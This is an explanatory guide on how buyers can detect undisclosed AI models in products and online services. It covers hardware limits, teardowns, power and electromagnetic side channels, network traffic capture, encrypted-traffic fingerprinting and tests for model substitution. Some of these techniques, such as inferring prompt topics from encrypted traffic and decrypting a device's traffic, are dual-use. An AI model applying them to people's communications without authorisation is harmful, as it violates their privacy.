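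Developers also scramble the names in their code to make it harder to copy. Liu and colleagues found that in the median app identified by AI Discriminator, about 12% of Java file names and 20% of folder names were scrambled. The existing tools they tried for recovering the original names either failed to run or gave poor results. Scrambling makes a text search less effective, but the search is still useful because most names remain readable.

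Searches can also miss a model that a developer has turned into machine code, because the result is an ordinary-looking program with no separate weights file and possibly no recognisable engine. *NeuroDeX* (Li, Meng and colleagues, 2025) describes a tool for reversing this process. It uses a decompiler and a language model to work out which calculation each part of the program performs, then runs the program to recover the weights and the order of the calculations.

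NeuroDeX recovered almost identical models from 88 of 96 test programs, which were made from 12 common models. After error correction, the recovered models' results matched those of the originals. The other eight programs came from *quantized* models, whose weights have been rounded to take up less space. The versions recovered from these ranked the expected answer first 72% of the time on average, and in the top five 86% of the time.

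These results are impressive, but Li and colleagues started with programs they knew contained models. A buyer's main problem is working out which programs to examine, and there may be thousands. NeuroDeX could help identify a model after something else, such as unexplained processor use, has raised suspicion.

A supplier determined to hide a model can probably defeat most of these searches, so when the buyer already distrusts the supplier, finding no model is weak evidence that there isn't one.

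Static analysis also can't find a model file that the product hasn't downloaded yet. Guyomard and colleagues note that a program can even download a model straight into memory each time without saving it. To find a model like that, the buyer has to run the product.

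## Testing a device: what it can hold, what it computes and what it sends

A buyer who can't read a product's files can still examine its hardware, measure it while it runs and record its network traffic. These methods are usually less exact than finding a model file, but they work even when the supplier has encrypted the files.

### What the hardware rules out

A short calculation can show that a device is too small for a language model:

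```text
size in bytes = number of weights × bits per weight ÷ 8
```

To fit models on small devices, developers often round each weight to 4 bits. A model with 8 billion weights then takes up 4 GB. A microcontroller with 2 MB of storage, which might run a thermostat, could hold at most 4 million weights, and fewer once the manufacturer has added the rest of the software. Gemma 3 1B, one of the small language models mentioned earlier, has about 250 times as many.

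The buyer can therefore tell, without trusting anyone, that the thermostat can't contain a general language model. It could still contain a classifier, since the weights files that Agyemang and colleagues found in Apple's software averaged only about 1.4 MB. It could also send its readings to a large model on a server.

A second calculation limits how fast a local language model can write. These models produce text one *token* at a time, a token being a word or part of a word. A *dense* model uses all its weights for every token, so the processor has to read all of them from memory each time. As *AI Hardware Accelerators for Large Language Models* (2026) explains, this gives a simple upper limit:

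```text
tokens per second ≤ memory bandwidth ÷ size of the weights
```

Memory bandwidth is the amount of data that the processor can read from memory each second. *Pipeline-Native Transformers* (2026) puts it at about 50 GB/s for an ordinary desktop or server processor. At that bandwidth, a 4 GB model could generate at most 12.5 tokens per second.

Well-designed systems get fairly close to the limit. *An MLIR-Based Compilation Method for Large Language Models* (2026) measured Alibaba's Qwen3.5 models on a chip for small devices. *Pushing up to the Limit of Memory Bandwidth and Capacity Utilization* (2025) describes fitting Llama 2 7B onto a board with 4 GB of memory, which the researchers managed only by running it without an operating system.

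| Model and hardware | Weights | Memory bandwidth | Upper limit, tokens per second | Measured |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 8 billion weights at 4 bits, ordinary processor | 4 GB | 50 GB/s | 12.5 | No figure |
| 8 billion weights at 4 bits, high-end phone | 4 GB | 77 GB/s | 19 | Similar |
| Qwen3.5, about 2 billion weights, small-device chip | 1.67 GB | 64 GB/s | 38 | 30 |
| Qwen3.5, about 9 billion weights, small-device chip | 5.39 GB | 64 GB/s | 12 | 9.84 |
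| Llama 2 7B, 4 GB board | 3.5 GB | 19 GB/s | 5.5 | About 5 |

Real speeds fall short partly because the processor also has to read a cache of the conversation so far, as *From Throughput to Deployment Decisions* (2026) points out. The Qwen3.5 files are larger than the first formula predicts at 4 bits, probably because developers store some parts of a model more precisely. Buyers should treat the formula's result as a minimum size.

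The Qwen3.5 results show that a capable language model can now fit in a few gigabytes. The smaller model accepts images as well as text and takes up less space than many films. Even the larger one generates text faster than most people read. A car dashboard or meeting-room display with 8 GB of memory could therefore contain such a model.

The speed limit has more exceptions than the storage limit. One is for *sparse* models, which use only some of their weights for each token. *Workload Identification with Physical Side Channels for AI Governance* (Gargiulo and Kulp, 2026) lists OpenAI's gpt-oss-20b as having 21 billion weights but using only 4 of its 32 "experts", or blocks of weights, at a time. The device still has to store every block, but it can generate text much faster than the model's total size suggests. The buyer should therefore divide the bandwidth by the amount of data the processor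 reads per token, not by the model's total size.

A shortage of memory rules out a fast language model but not necessarily a slow one, because a device can read some of the weights from storage for each token. *LazyWeights* (2026) gives the resulting delay as the amount of data read divided by the storage speed. If a device had to read 2 GB at 0.5 GB/s, each token would take at least four seconds. That would be too slow for a conversation, but the device could write a 200-token summary of the day's events overnight in about 13 minutes.

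Finally, the limit in the table applies to a device that produces one token each time it reads the weights. A device can exceed it by answering several users at once, or by using a small model to guess the next few tokens and a large one to check them together.

### Taking the device apart

A supplier's specifications may not say how much memory a device has or whether it contains a microphone. To find out, the buyer can commission a *teardown*. An examiner opens a sample unit, lifts off any metal shields, reads the part numbers on the chips, and looks them up in the manufacturers' datasheets. The examiner also traces cables and antennas to find cameras, microphones and radios. The buyer then checks whether the device's stated function explains each part.

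| Part | Why it matters | Innocent explanation |
|---|---|---|
| AI accelerator, as a separate chip or part of the processor | Runs local models faster and with less power | The manufacturer bought a standard chip and doesn't use this part |
| Several gigabytes of memory and storage | Leaves room for a language model | The product stores video or maps |
| Camera or microphone | Supplies images or speech to a model | The product scans barcodes or makes calls |
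| Cellular, Wi-Fi or Bluetooth radio | Can connect to a remote model or download a local one | The product takes card payments or reports faults |

Buyers can often learn more from a missing part than from a suspicious one. A vending machine without a camera can't estimate customers' ages from their faces unless another device sends it pictures. A missing AI accelerator is much weaker evidence, because ordinary processors can also run models, including small language models.

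Examining the University of Waterloo's vending machines before installation would have revealed the camera in each one. The university could then have asked why a snack machine needed a camera, although the camera alone wouldn't have proved that the machine detected faces.

A teardown may destroy the sample or void its warranty, which is another reason to agree test rights in the contract. Some chips have no readable markings, and one package can combine a processor, memory and a radio. Manufacturers also change parts between production runs without changing the product's name, so a large buyer should pick the sample from the delivered stock instead of accepting one from the supplier.

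### Undeclared radios and the Norwegian bus test

Two well-known inspections of purchased equipment show what physical examination can find. Both concerned communications hardware and neither found AI.

In May 2025 Reuters reported that US experts had taken apart Chinese-made solar inverters and found communication devices that the product documents didn't list. Inverters connect solar panels to the electricity grid. Utilities usually put them behind firewalls to block direct communication with China, but an extra radio could bypass the firewall. Over the previous nine months, the experts had also found undocumented devices, including cellular radios, in batteries from several Chinese suppliers.

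The public evidence is thin. Reuters relied on two anonymous people, who wouldn't name the manufacturers or say how many devices the experts had found. Reuters couldn't establish how many inverters and batteries the experts had examined, so nobody can work out how common the problem is. The US Department of Energy did not confirm the findings. It said that undisclosed functions may not be malicious but that buyers need to understand what they are getting.

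The department also said work was under way to close gaps in disclosure through SBOMs and contract terms. SBOMs would be a weak remedy for this problem because they list software and a radio is hardware. At best, an SBOM might include the program that operates the radio.

US regulators have since taken a blunter approach, banning new inverter models based on where they are made, whether or not a teardown would find anything wrong. In July 2026 the Federal Communications Commission (FCC) barred new models of foreign-made inverters that it had not already certified (Touriño Jacobo, 2026, *US government bans foreign-produced inverters*). In August it extended the ban to wired inverters and exempted inverters eligible for a US manufacturing tax credit (Touriño Jacobo, 2026, *FCC removes eligible 45X inverters from foreign ban, includes wired ones*).

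The Norwegian case is much better documented. In 2025 Ruter, the public transport authority for the Oslo area, tested a new electric bus from the Chinese manufacturer Yutong and a three-year-old bus from the Dutch company VDL. According to ScandAsia, Ruter tested them in a disused mine that blocked all radio signals, so engineers could examine the buses without outside interference.

Ruter's *We have conducted a comprehensive safety test of electric buses* reports that the cameras on the two buses tested, a Yutong and a VDL, were not connected to the internet. However, the Yutong bus had a Romanian SIM card through which the manufacturer could reach the control system for the battery and power supply. In theory, Yutong could use this access to stop the bus. The VDL bus couldn't receive software updates remotely.

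Yutong disputed this, saying that it installs updates only with the operator's approval and that they don't affect vehicle control, according to Sustainable Bus' *Yutong responds to cybersecurity allegations*. Ruter's account of what the connection can reach deserves more weight, because Ruter inspected the bus. But Ruter had no evidence that anyone had misused the connection, and called the danger theoretical. The findings still worried other operators. Denmark's largest public transport company planned to tighten its security in September 2026, according to Hemmer-Hansen's *Norske forskere kørte en kinesisk elbus ind i en nedlagt mine* (2026).

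An undeclared radio may be the only part a device needs to use a remote AI model, and it can carry data that never passes through the buyer's own network.

### Watching the device run

Monitoring a device while it runs can show whether it does more work than its function seems to require. On a computer or an unlocked phone, ordinary system tools list the memory and processor time that each program uses, and sometimes its use of an AI accelerator. If a program uses another 3 GB of memory when someone clicks "Summarise", it has probably loaded a language model.

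Locked devices don't offer such tools, but the buyer can measure their power use from outside. A cheap plug-in meter may detect a language model that runs for several seconds. A classifier can finish in a few milliseconds, so detecting one usually requires a faster instrument.

The examiner should change one input at a time and repeat each test. To check an advertising screen for face analysis, for example, they could measure its power use with nobody there, with a person facing it, with the same person facing away, and with a cardboard box moving past. The box is included because video compression can also use more power when something moves. If power use rises consistently for a face but not for the box or the back of a head, the screen is probably processing faces differently.

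This test would miss some models. At Waterloo, the object detector processed every video frame, so its workload might have stayed almost constant whether or not anyone was there. The model that estimated age and gender would have been easier to spot because it ran only after the detector found a face. To measure the detector's workload, the examiner would have had to disconnect the camera or stop the program.

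Language models have a more distinctive pattern of activity. In *Physical Side-Channel Attacks on Edge LLMs*, Alhalawani, Acar and colleagues (2026) ran Llama 3.2 1B on a Raspberry Pi 5, a small general-purpose computer, and recorded its electromagnetic emissions with a probe above the processor. The recording showed one long block of activity while the model read the prompt, then a shorter repeating block for each further token. The trace for a single token showed the model's 16 layers one after another.

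A buyer could look for the same pattern in a product that accepts text. A longer question should lengthen the first block, and a longer answer should add more short blocks. But Alhalawani and colleagues knew which model was running, chose the board and fixed the processor's speed to get clean recordings. An unfamiliar device that is also playing video and updating its screen would produce a much messier trace.

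### Recognising AI from power use

Software can learn to recognise AI workloads from electrical measurements. Gargiulo and Kulp clamped a current probe around the power cable of one Nvidia H200, a powerful data-centre chip, and made 930 five-second recordings. The recordings covered 17 language models and 25 non-AI workloads, including an idle chip. The researchers then trained a classifier to tell whether each recording showed a model being trained, a model in use or neither.

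The classifier was correct about 97% of the time on language models it had not seen in training. The equipment doesn't need to be very fast. When Gargiulo and Kulp kept only one measurement in 256, accuracy was still 94.6%. That left about 38,000 measurements per second, which is similar to the rate at which a computer's sound card records.

Results would probably be worse on a purchased device. More than half of the recordings showed training, which few products do. The recordings of models in use showed them reading text but not writing any. The non-AI workloads were mostly simple operations, such as sorting numbers or copying memory, repeated continuously. Real products switch between many tasks, some of which, such as processing video, may look more like AI. The researchers also found that an operator could make training harder to detect by disguising it.

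*Verifying Declared AI Workloads from GPU Supply Current* (Kimpson, 2026) tests a method that doesn't need examples of the forbidden workload. The method records the GPU's supply current while the machine does its declared work, then raises an alarm when the current no longer looks like those recordings. On one H200 GPU, it caught all 188 episodes of hidden training in the main test and raised one false alarm in 8.8 hours of permitted work.

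This approach would suit a buyer who knows what a device should do but not what an undisclosed model would look like. However, it depends heavily on what the original recordings include. When Kimpson left idle periods out of them, the monitor was in alarm for 99.97% of the chip's idle time. It is worse to include activity that the monitor should detect. If a device already contains an undisclosed model on delivery, the buyer will record it as part of normal operation, and the monitor may never raise an alarm about it. Kimpson showed that including training in the original recordings could make the monitor miss later training without any sign of a fault.

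There is some evidence that the methods can work on different chips. Kimpson cites a study in which Rahman and Tajdari identified training with 98% accuracy across nine types of GPU, using measurements reported by the chips. But those were also known processors running known workloads. None of these studies tested an unfamiliar commercial device, such as a camera or a vending machine, and there seem to be no published figures for how often the technique would find an undisclosed model in one. Power measurements are a reasonable way to decide which device to take apart, but for now they are poor evidence for accusing a supplier.

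### Recording network traffic

Capturing a device's network traffic is usually easier than measuring its emissions. The buyer connects the device through a router they control and saves a copy of every *packet*, the small unit in which data travels. Free programs such as Wireshark can display the packets. A device with its own cellular connection bypasses the router, so the buyer should check for one first.

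Most products encrypt their traffic, which hides the content but leaves a lot visible:

| What the buyer can see | What it may reveal | How it can mislead |
|---|---|---|
| Destination name | An AI provider, such as `api.anthropic.com` | The name may belong to the supplier, or the device may hide it |
| Destination address | The company that operates the server | Many businesses rent servers from the same cloud company |
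| Amount of data | Whether the device is sending text, sound or video | The device may compress the data or add padding |
| Timing | Which event caused the transmission | The device may save data and send it later |

A device normally looks up a server's name before connecting to it, and then repeats the name at the start of the encrypted connection. Newer protocols can encrypt both steps. When they do, the buyer may see only a numerical address belonging to Amazon or Google.

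The amount of data a device sends can help to distinguish a local model from a remote one. Ten seconds of speech compressed to 16 kilobits per second takes up about 20 KB. A transcript of the same speech might take up only 200 bytes, plus some overhead. If a voice-controlled device sends about 20 KB after every ten-second request, it's probably sending the recording to a server. If it sends much less, it may be recognising the words locally.

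A device that uploads little data may therefore still contain a model. The Waterloo machines reported only a few facts about each sale, such as the time and the customer's estimated age and gender. Someone who checked only for video uploads could have missed the face detection.

The examiner can strengthen the evidence by saying the same sentence 20 times at random moments and checking whether an upload follows each time. If uploads always follow the sentence but not other sounds of similar length, such as a cough or a slammed door, the device is probably detecting speech before it sends anything.

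Encryption still prevents the buyer from checking exactly what a device sends. Writing about connected buses in *ITS Norway mener*, Breivik and Tjomsland (2026) note that a modern vehicle usually reports its position and the condition of its systems, but could also collect video, sound or the identities of nearby phones. They say operators must trust the manufacturer about which data it takes and what it does with them.

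A buyer can sometimes read encrypted traffic by installing their own security certificate on the device and sending the traffic through a computer that decrypts it. This works on many laptops and some phones. Locked devices usually don't allow it, and a well-protected app may block the connection. The contract could instead require the supplier to provide a test version of the product that records what it sends before encryption.

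### Recognising language models in encrypted traffic

Language models often leave a recognisable pattern in encrypted traffic because many services *stream* their answers, sending each piece of text as the model produces it. The buyer sees a series of small packets instead of one large download. *Exposing LLM User Privacy via Traffic Fingerprint Analysis* (2025) explains that longer words tend to make larger packets. The gaps between packets partly reflect how fast the model works.

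Packet sizes and timing can reveal the topic of a question sent to a language model, even when the traffic is encrypted. *Whisper Leak* (2025) used a language model to write 100 versions of a question about whether money laundering is legal, then sent each version 100 times to the model being tested. It trained software to distinguish this traffic from that of 11,716 unrelated questions, using only packet sizes and timing. The paper was about eavesdropping, but the same leak can help buyers investigate their own equipment.

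In *A Large-Scale Benchmark and Risk Assessment of Traffic Analysis Attacks*, Pouryousef, Lopez and colleagues (2026) tried to identify language models from their encrypted traffic. They sent 60 prompts, 100 times each, to each of 10 models and recorded the traffic. Their software ignored the server's address and used only the size, direction and timing of the packets. It identified the right model 97.7% of the time. The most useful clue was the pattern of *bursts*, which are uninterrupted runs of packets in the same direction.

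The result depends heavily on the test conditions. The researchers ran the models on their own server and had recordings of each one to compare against. In one part of the study, accuracy fell from 93.2% to 69.5% when they reworded the prompts. With 20 models to choose from, accuracy was about 92%. The software could tell apart two models built on the same base model, so Pouryousef and colleagues interpret the pattern as a fingerprint of the whole service, not just the model's design. A provider could therefore change the fingerprint by changing its server software.

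A more basic problem for a buyer is that the software had to choose between known language models, and the test included no ordinary web traffic, so it doesn't show how often a stock update or a live news feed would be mistaken for a language model. A buyer who sees a slow stream of small packets after each question has good reason to suspect a language model, but no study here measures how often that suspicion would be wrong.

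Agents may leave a longer traffic pattern because they call a model repeatedly and use tools between calls. One user request might lead to ten exchanges with a model, separated by database searches. Pouryousef and colleagues recorded traffic from groups of agents working together and identified which of ten kinds of task they were doing with up to 90.7% accuracy. Accuracy dropped to 52% when the agents shared work differently from those in the training data. The researchers already knew that all the traffic came from agents, so these figures don't show how well the method would detect an undisclosed agent.

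### When the supplier's server is in between

Many products don't contact a model provider directly. They send data to the supplier's server, which passes it on:

```text
device  ----------->  supplier's server  ----------->  model provider
        buyer can                          buyer can't
        record this                        record this
```

The connection between the supplier and the provider runs between two data centres, so it never crosses the buyer's network. The buyer sees the supplier's name and address, and neither would change if the supplier switched to another company's model.

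If the supplier forwards each piece of text immediately, the device still receives a stream of small packets, and some of the rhythm may remain. This suggests that a language model is involved but is weak evidence about which one, because the supplier's server can change the size and timing of the packets. If the supplier waits for the complete answer and sends it all at once, the rhythm disappears.

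The buyer can still compare how long different requests take. A language model usually takes longer to write more text, while a database search often takes about the same time whether the result is short or long. Timing is only a clue, since a busy server can cause similar delays. To identify the model that the supplier's server uses, the buyer may have to study the product's answers, if it returns any.

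### Disconnecting the device

An offline test can help establish where a model runs. The buyer disconnects the device from every network, restarts it and tries each feature. If the device can still answer unfamiliar questions in fluent text, it almost certainly contains a local language model. The buyer can check this result against the capacity calculation. A device with 2 MB of storage couldn't do this by itself, so the buyer should look for a connection they missed.

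A feature that stops working offline is harder to interpret. The model may be remote, but the product could also be checking its licence or looking up ordinary data. Comparing the offline result with the network recording helps to separate the possibilities:

| Offline | Online | Likely explanation |
|---|---|---|
| The feature works | No related traffic | A local model or an ordinary program |
| The feature works | A small upload after each event | Local processing, with results sent to a server |
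| The feature stops | A large upload of sound or images before each result | Remote processing, possibly by a model |
| The feature stops | A small upload before each result | Remote processing of text, a database search or a licence check |

It is hard to make sure that the device is really offline. After the Norwegian bus tests, Breivik and Tjomsland disputed suggestions that operators could simply remove the SIM card. They said Ruter had never demonstrated this and had only proposed isolating the whole communications module. They pointed out that a vehicle can also receive signals through Wi-Fi, Bluetooth or satellite, and that a tiny built-in SIM could be hidden on a circuit board. Further tests were planned for autumn 2026.

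A buyer can test a small device in a shielded box that blocks radio signals. To check the shielding, the examiner can first put a phone in the box and call it. The examiner should also block or disconnect any network cable, and use a battery or a filtered power supply, because some devices can send data through electrical wiring.

The device may save data while it is offline and send them when the connection returns. A device with a microphone could record all afternoon in the box, pass every test, and upload the recordings that evening for a remote model to transcribe. The buyer should therefore start recording network traffic before reconnecting the device and continue for at least a day. If the device uploads much more after an afternoon of conversation than after a silent one, it was probably listening.

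## Testing an online service whose servers the buyer cannot inspect

A buyer testing an online service can observe only its inputs, outputs and response times, plus anything the supplier puts in writing, because there are no files to unpack or device to take apart. This evidence is often enough to show that the service uses a language model, and sometimes to identify which one. It is harder to show that the supplier has changed the model since the contract began.

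### Finding out whether a model is involved

The easiest place to start is the supplier's list of *subprocessors*, the subcontractors that handle customers' personal data. EU data protection law requires suppliers to get a customer's authorisation before using one, so many business services publish a list. An entry for OpenAI or Anthropic is a strong clue. But a supplier that runs a downloaded model on its own servers has no model provider to list. If it rents a model through Amazon or Microsoft, the list may name only that company, which would be on it anyway. The list also needn't cover subcontractors that handle only non-personal data, such as engineering drawings.

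Model names can also leak through the interface. Web pages often receive more data than they display, and a browser's developer tools can show the rest. The buyer can look for a field called `model`, or for error messages about a maximum number of tokens.

A third approach is to send inputs that a person, a fixed program and a language model would handle differently. These examples would suit a help desk that supposedly has human staff or follows simple rules:

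| Input | Person | Fixed program | Language model |
|---|---|---|---|
| A long, rambling complaint in Welsh | Takes minutes or asks for a translation | Sends a stock reply | Replies fluently and to the point within seconds |
| The same question ten times, from different accounts | Pastes the same reply or notices the repetition | Gives identical answers | Often gives the same advice in different words |
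| A request for a random number from 1 to 100, made 30 times | Soon objects | Ignores the request | Often picks the same few numbers |

The random-number test draws on *One Token Is Enough* (Bruckner, 2026), which found that language models are very bad at choosing numbers at random. Asked for a random number 30 times, Alibaba's Qwen3-Max answered 42 every time.

There seem to be no published error rates for using such inputs to tell models from people or fixed programs. The repetition test can fail if the supplier stores old answers or turns down the model's randomness. Human staff may also be pasting the questions into a chatbot. The most convincing sign of a model is a fast, relevant answer to an input nobody could have prepared for.

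Classifiers are harder to detect because they may return only a score. To test a loan service, for example, the buyer can submit two fictional applications that differ only in the wording of the free-text box. If the scores differ, software is probably processing the text, though it could be matching words against a simple keyword list. If the service neither shows the score nor visibly acts on it, no outside test will detect the classifier.

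### Identifying the model

Asking a model for its name is not a reliable way to identify it. *LLMmap* (Pasquini, Kornaropoulos and Ateniese, 2024) lists 14 models that gave the wrong answer, including Microsoft's Phi-3 mini, which identified itself as GPT-4. Newer models may answer more accurately, but a supplier can still instruct a model to give any name.

Fingerprinting relies on patterns in a model's answers that are harder to disguise. LLMmap, an early tool, sends a service eight questions and uses a classifier to identify the model from the answers. The questions are meant to draw different answers from different models but consistent answers from the same model under different settings. In the LLMmap paper's own tests, the tool distinguished 42 model versions with over 95% accuracy.

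LLMmap did much worse in a later test on models set up like finished products. Suppliers usually give a model a *system prompt*, a set of hidden instructions such as "You are a pharmacy assistant. Discuss only medicines." *AdaptPrint* (Li, Zhang and Meng, 2026) tested LLMmap on 12 models behind 18 different system prompts. LLMmap picked the right model from 27 candidates 36.6% of the time. It was right 57.4% of the time when it had examples recorded under other system prompts and only 12 candidates to choose from.

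LLMmap's questions also look suspicious. One filter blocked four of the eight as attempts to get around safety rules, and another rejected 133 of 144 as off-topic for the service.

The researchers' own tool, also called AdaptPrint, starts with an ordinary question that suits the service:

1. A language model writes a question on the service's subject, worded so that most answers will follow a similar line of reasoning.
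2. The tool sends the question to the service and to every candidate model, then compares their answers.
3. It gives each candidate the beginning of the service's answer and asks it to continue. It then compares each continuation with what the service actually wrote.
4. It asks the service and the candidates a follow-up question about the service's first answer.
5. It scores the candidates on similarity of meaning and shared phrases, and picks the one with the highest total.

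The third step helps because a long passage in the hidden model's own style can outweigh the system prompt. With three starting questions (six messages to the service), AdaptPrint identified the right model 80.6% of the time and ranked it in the top three 90.3% of the time. Each identification cost about four US cents.

Li and colleagues also tried two *fine-tuned* versions of Llama 3.1 8B, which other developers had trained further for coding and medicine. AdaptPrint traced them to the original model in eight of 12 tests.

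These are good results for identifying a hidden model, but one answer in five was wrong. AdaptPrint can also identify the true model only if it is among the candidates. It can decline to answer when the top two scores are close, but this also rejects some correct matches. Its only trial on a live commercial service used a chatbot whose model was already public. A buyer could reasonably use a match to ask the supplier whether the model is Qwen, but not to accuse the supplier of lying.

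Bruckner's method suits buyers who can send a model very short requests, usually through a programming interface. It uses ten tasks, such as naming a random colour or flipping a coin, in four languages and compares how often each answer appears. Bruckner collected these frequencies from 165 models for $34.44 in total.

Bruckner tested whether the patterns could verify a model's identity by splitting each model's answers into two halves and comparing the halves with each other and with other models' answers. With the full set of tasks, the *equal error rate* was 7.3%, which means the test can be set to reject 7.3% of true matches and accept 7.3% of false ones. With about 120 requests, the rate rose to 10.6%.

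| Method | Requests to the service | Models covered | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| LLMmap, original test | 8 | 42 | Over 95% correct |
| LLMmap, behind 18 system prompts | 8 | 27 | 36.6% correct |
| AdaptPrint, behind 18 system prompts | 6 | 27 | 80.6% correct |
| Bruckner's one-word answers, short version | About 120 | 165 | 10.6% equal error rate |
| Bruckner's one-word answers, full version | About 600 | 165 | 7.3% equal error rate |

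The last two rows measure the easier task of checking a claimed identity rather than picking one model from a list. Bruckner also left out models that can't answer without a hidden reasoning phase, so the method may not work on some leading models. A pharmacy assistant might also refuse to name a colour.

The survey found that Palmyra X5, which the company Writer markets as its own model, gave answers almost indistinguishable from those of an open-weight Qwen model. The distance between them was 0.141 on a scale from 0 to 1. Two samples from the same model typically differed by 0.140, and samples from different models by 0.463. Bruckner presents this as a statistical finding, not an accusation.

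The method can also miss a model's origin. Nvidia built one of its Nemotron models from Llama 3.3, but that model's answers were closer to Qwen's than to any Llama model's, so heavy further training can erase the pattern. Across the survey, the closest match belonged to the right family only 59.5% of the time, compared with 18.4% by chance.

Lighter changes to a model leave more evidence. *Every Model Leaves a Trace* (Modarres, Tourajmehr and colleagues, 2026) reports that fingerprints could still be detected in lightly fine-tuned models and in models trained to imitate others. The fingerprints weakened when the researchers reworded the text, which a supplier's server could do automatically. Another method, described in *SetPrint* (2026), traces altered models from their answers alone and outperformed comparable methods on a standard test. *Reading Between the Lines* (Shao, Li and colleagues,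 2025) notes that methods that rely only on answers are less reliable than those that examine a model's weights.

Model developers can also train a model to give a particular answer to a secret question. *One Sequence Is Enough* (2026) includes this technique in its survey of methods. A buyer who strongly suspects that a service uses a particular model could therefore ask that model's developer to check.

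### How users found Kimi behind Composer 2

In March 2026 Cursor, a US company that makes AI coding tools, launched a model called Composer 2. Users soon spotted references to Kimi, a model from the Chinese company Moonshot AI, and pressed Cursor for an explanation, according to eWeek's *Cursor AI Admits Composer 2 Was Built on Moonshot’s Kimi Tech* (2026). Their evidence was the leaked name rather than a technical fingerprint of the model.

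Cursor confirmed that it had built its model from Kimi K2.5, whose weights are public. Lee Robinson, a Cursor vice president, said that only about a quarter of the computation behind the final model came from the base and the rest came from Cursor's own training. Those shares describe how much work Cursor added, not how independent the model is of Kimi, because Cursor's training began with Kimi's weights.

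On 20 March, Moonshot congratulated Cursor and said that Cursor used Kimi through Fireworks AI, a company that hosts models, under "an authorized commercial partnership" (statement reproduced in Willison, 2026). A subprocessor list could therefore have included Fireworks but not Moonshot.

Cursor's *Composer 2 Technical Report* (2026) names Kimi K2.5 as the base model and says the company chose it after comparing models on coding knowledge and other measures. Cursor first trained it further on a large dataset of mostly code. It then used *reinforcement learning*, in which the model attempted coding tasks and received rewards for good solutions.

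Cursor openly advertised Composer 2 as an agent model that can edit files and run commands in Cursor's software. But customers didn't know where the model came from, which matters to a buyer that bans models from particular developers or countries.

Fingerprinting might not have revealed that Composer 2 was built on Kimi. Cursor's further training was extensive, and the Nemotron example shows that such training can hide a model's family. Enough of Kimi's style may have survived for fingerprinting to detect it, but Bruckner's survey didn't test Composer 2. Cursor named Kimi K2.5 in its announcement of the next version, Composer 2.5.

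### Checking whether the supplier has swapped the model

Even if a buyer knows which model a service is supposed to use, the supplier can quietly send some or all requests to another one. *Are You Getting What You Pay For?* (Cai, Shi and colleagues, 2025) calls this *model substitution*. The replacement might be a smaller model from the same family, a fine-tuned version or a model from another developer. A cheaper replacement saves the supplier money on every request, but substitution can also be accidental.

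Most audits have examined companies that resell access to named models. Bruckner cites a study by Gao, Liang and Guestrin in which 11 of 31 commercial services offering Llama models gave answers that didn't statistically match the original models'. Some of these mismatches may have had innocent causes, such as different software or compressed weights.

*Behavioral Consistency and Transparency Analysis on Large Language Model API Gateways* (Lin, Wan and colleagues, 2026) tested ten *gateways*, which offer models from several developers through one interface. The researchers asked each model 55 questions, five times each, and trained classifiers on features such as the number of reasoning steps and whether the final answer was correct. On OpenAI's own service, the classifiers recognised 97% of GPT-5's answers. On the nine gateways that offered GPT-5, they recognised between 13% and 97%.

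The same study shows that response time is weak evidence of substitution. One gateway's response times for GPT-4o varied much more than OpenAI's, yet the classifiers matched 93% of its answers to GPT-4o. Another gateway's response times were almost as steady as OpenAI's, but only 62% of its answers matched, so a buyer relying on timing alone would have suspected the wrong gateway. Pouryousef and colleagues also found that the type of question affects response time, so a buyer should compare response times for the same questions.

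*Real Money, Fake Models* (Zhang, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) audited unofficial resellers, which often serve customers in countries where the models' developers don't sell access. The researchers found 17 such services in the code behind 187 academic papers. They used LLMmap to test eight models on each of three resellers. Eleven of the 24 combinations of model and reseller failed the test, including two where a request for GPT-5 appeared to go to GLM-4-9B, a much smaller model.

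Some of those failures may be errors by the tool. LLMmap identified one reseller's GPT-5 mini as the full GPT-5, and another's GPT-4o mini as GPT-4o. A reseller would normally pay more to supply the full models, so fraud is an odd explanation. When Zhang and colleagues set up six services of their own, LLMmap wrongly flagged 3% of honest ones and missed 5% of substitutions. It did far better here than on models behind system prompts, probably because the resellers and test services offered fairly direct access to the models.

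A matching fingerprint doesn't guarantee the same quality either. All three resellers passed the LLMmap check for Gemini 2.5 Flash, but on a set of medical exam questions, the model scored about 37% through the resellers and 84% through Google. The study could not establish why. A buyer who relies on a service for medical or legal work should test its accuracy on that work, even if the fingerprint matches.

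### A substitution test step by step

*API-TAIL* (Mei, Tian and colleagues, 2026) describes a test for catching a provider that substitutes a different model for only some of its answers. The buyer must be able to run the advertised model independently, so the test works for open-weight models such as Qwen but not for GPT or Claude.

1. The buyer sends 200 different prompts to the service and saves one answer to each.

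2. The buyer runs the advertised model on those answers. For every token, the model calculates how likely it would have been to choose that token next. An unlikely token has a high *surprise*, defined as the negative logarithm of its probability.

3. The software turns each answer's total surprise into a score:

   ```text
   score = (actual surprise - expected surprise) / expected spread
   ```

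   The expected values come from the model's own predictions. An answer that the advertised model wrote should usually score near zero.

4. Honest providers use different settings, particularly *temperature*, which controls how random the answers are. The software finds the temperature that brings the 200 scores as close as possible to zero on average. This removes differences that affect all the answers, but an answer from another model should still stand out.

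5. The software counts the answers that score above 3 and compares the count with a limit. To set the limit, the buyer runs the advertised model under 16 to 19 ordinary configurations and observes how many high scores each produces. In one version of the test, the limit was seven, so eight high scores would raise an alarm.

The researchers designed the test to give false alarms at most 5% of the time under any configuration they had anticipated. They then tried it on 26 commercial services they judged honest from the providers' descriptions and a short check. The highest false-alarm rate was 6.9%, and most were below 1%. An audit cost less than 16 cents in fees and took up to eight minutes on a powerful AI chip.

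How well the test detects substitution depends on the replacement. These are the results when a provider swapped 10% of the answers from Qwen3.8-27B, using 200 fairly long responses:

| Replacement model | Chance of detection |
|---|---|
| DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash | 100% |
| Qwen3.8-Flash, a smaller relative | 99% |
| Qwen3.6-27B, the previous version, from an outside provider | 69% |
| Qwen3.6-27B from its developer's own platform | 0% |

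The last two rows involve the same model, so the settings on the replacement's server can determine whether the test works. On the developer's platform, the detection rate reached only 7% even when the provider swapped a quarter of the answers.

System prompts are a bigger problem for most buyers. One provider openly added its own system prompt to Qwen, and the test flagged the service in 79% of audits with short answers and 99% with longer ones. Most finished products have a system prompt, so buyers can use this test to check direct access to a model, but not to check a product such as a help-desk assistant.

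### Where statistical tests fail

Older tests struggle with partial swaps. *Model equality testing* compares a batch of answers from the service with a batch from the genuine model. The *rank-based uniformity test* checks where each answer from the service falls among many answers that the genuine model gives to the same prompt. Mei and colleagues adjusted both to tolerate normal differences between honest providers. With 200 requests, neither detected a 10% swap in the main tests. Mei and colleagues were comparing these adjusted tests with their own method, so the results may somewhat overstate its advantage. But Zhang and colleagues found that model equality testing missed 18.67% of complete substitutions.

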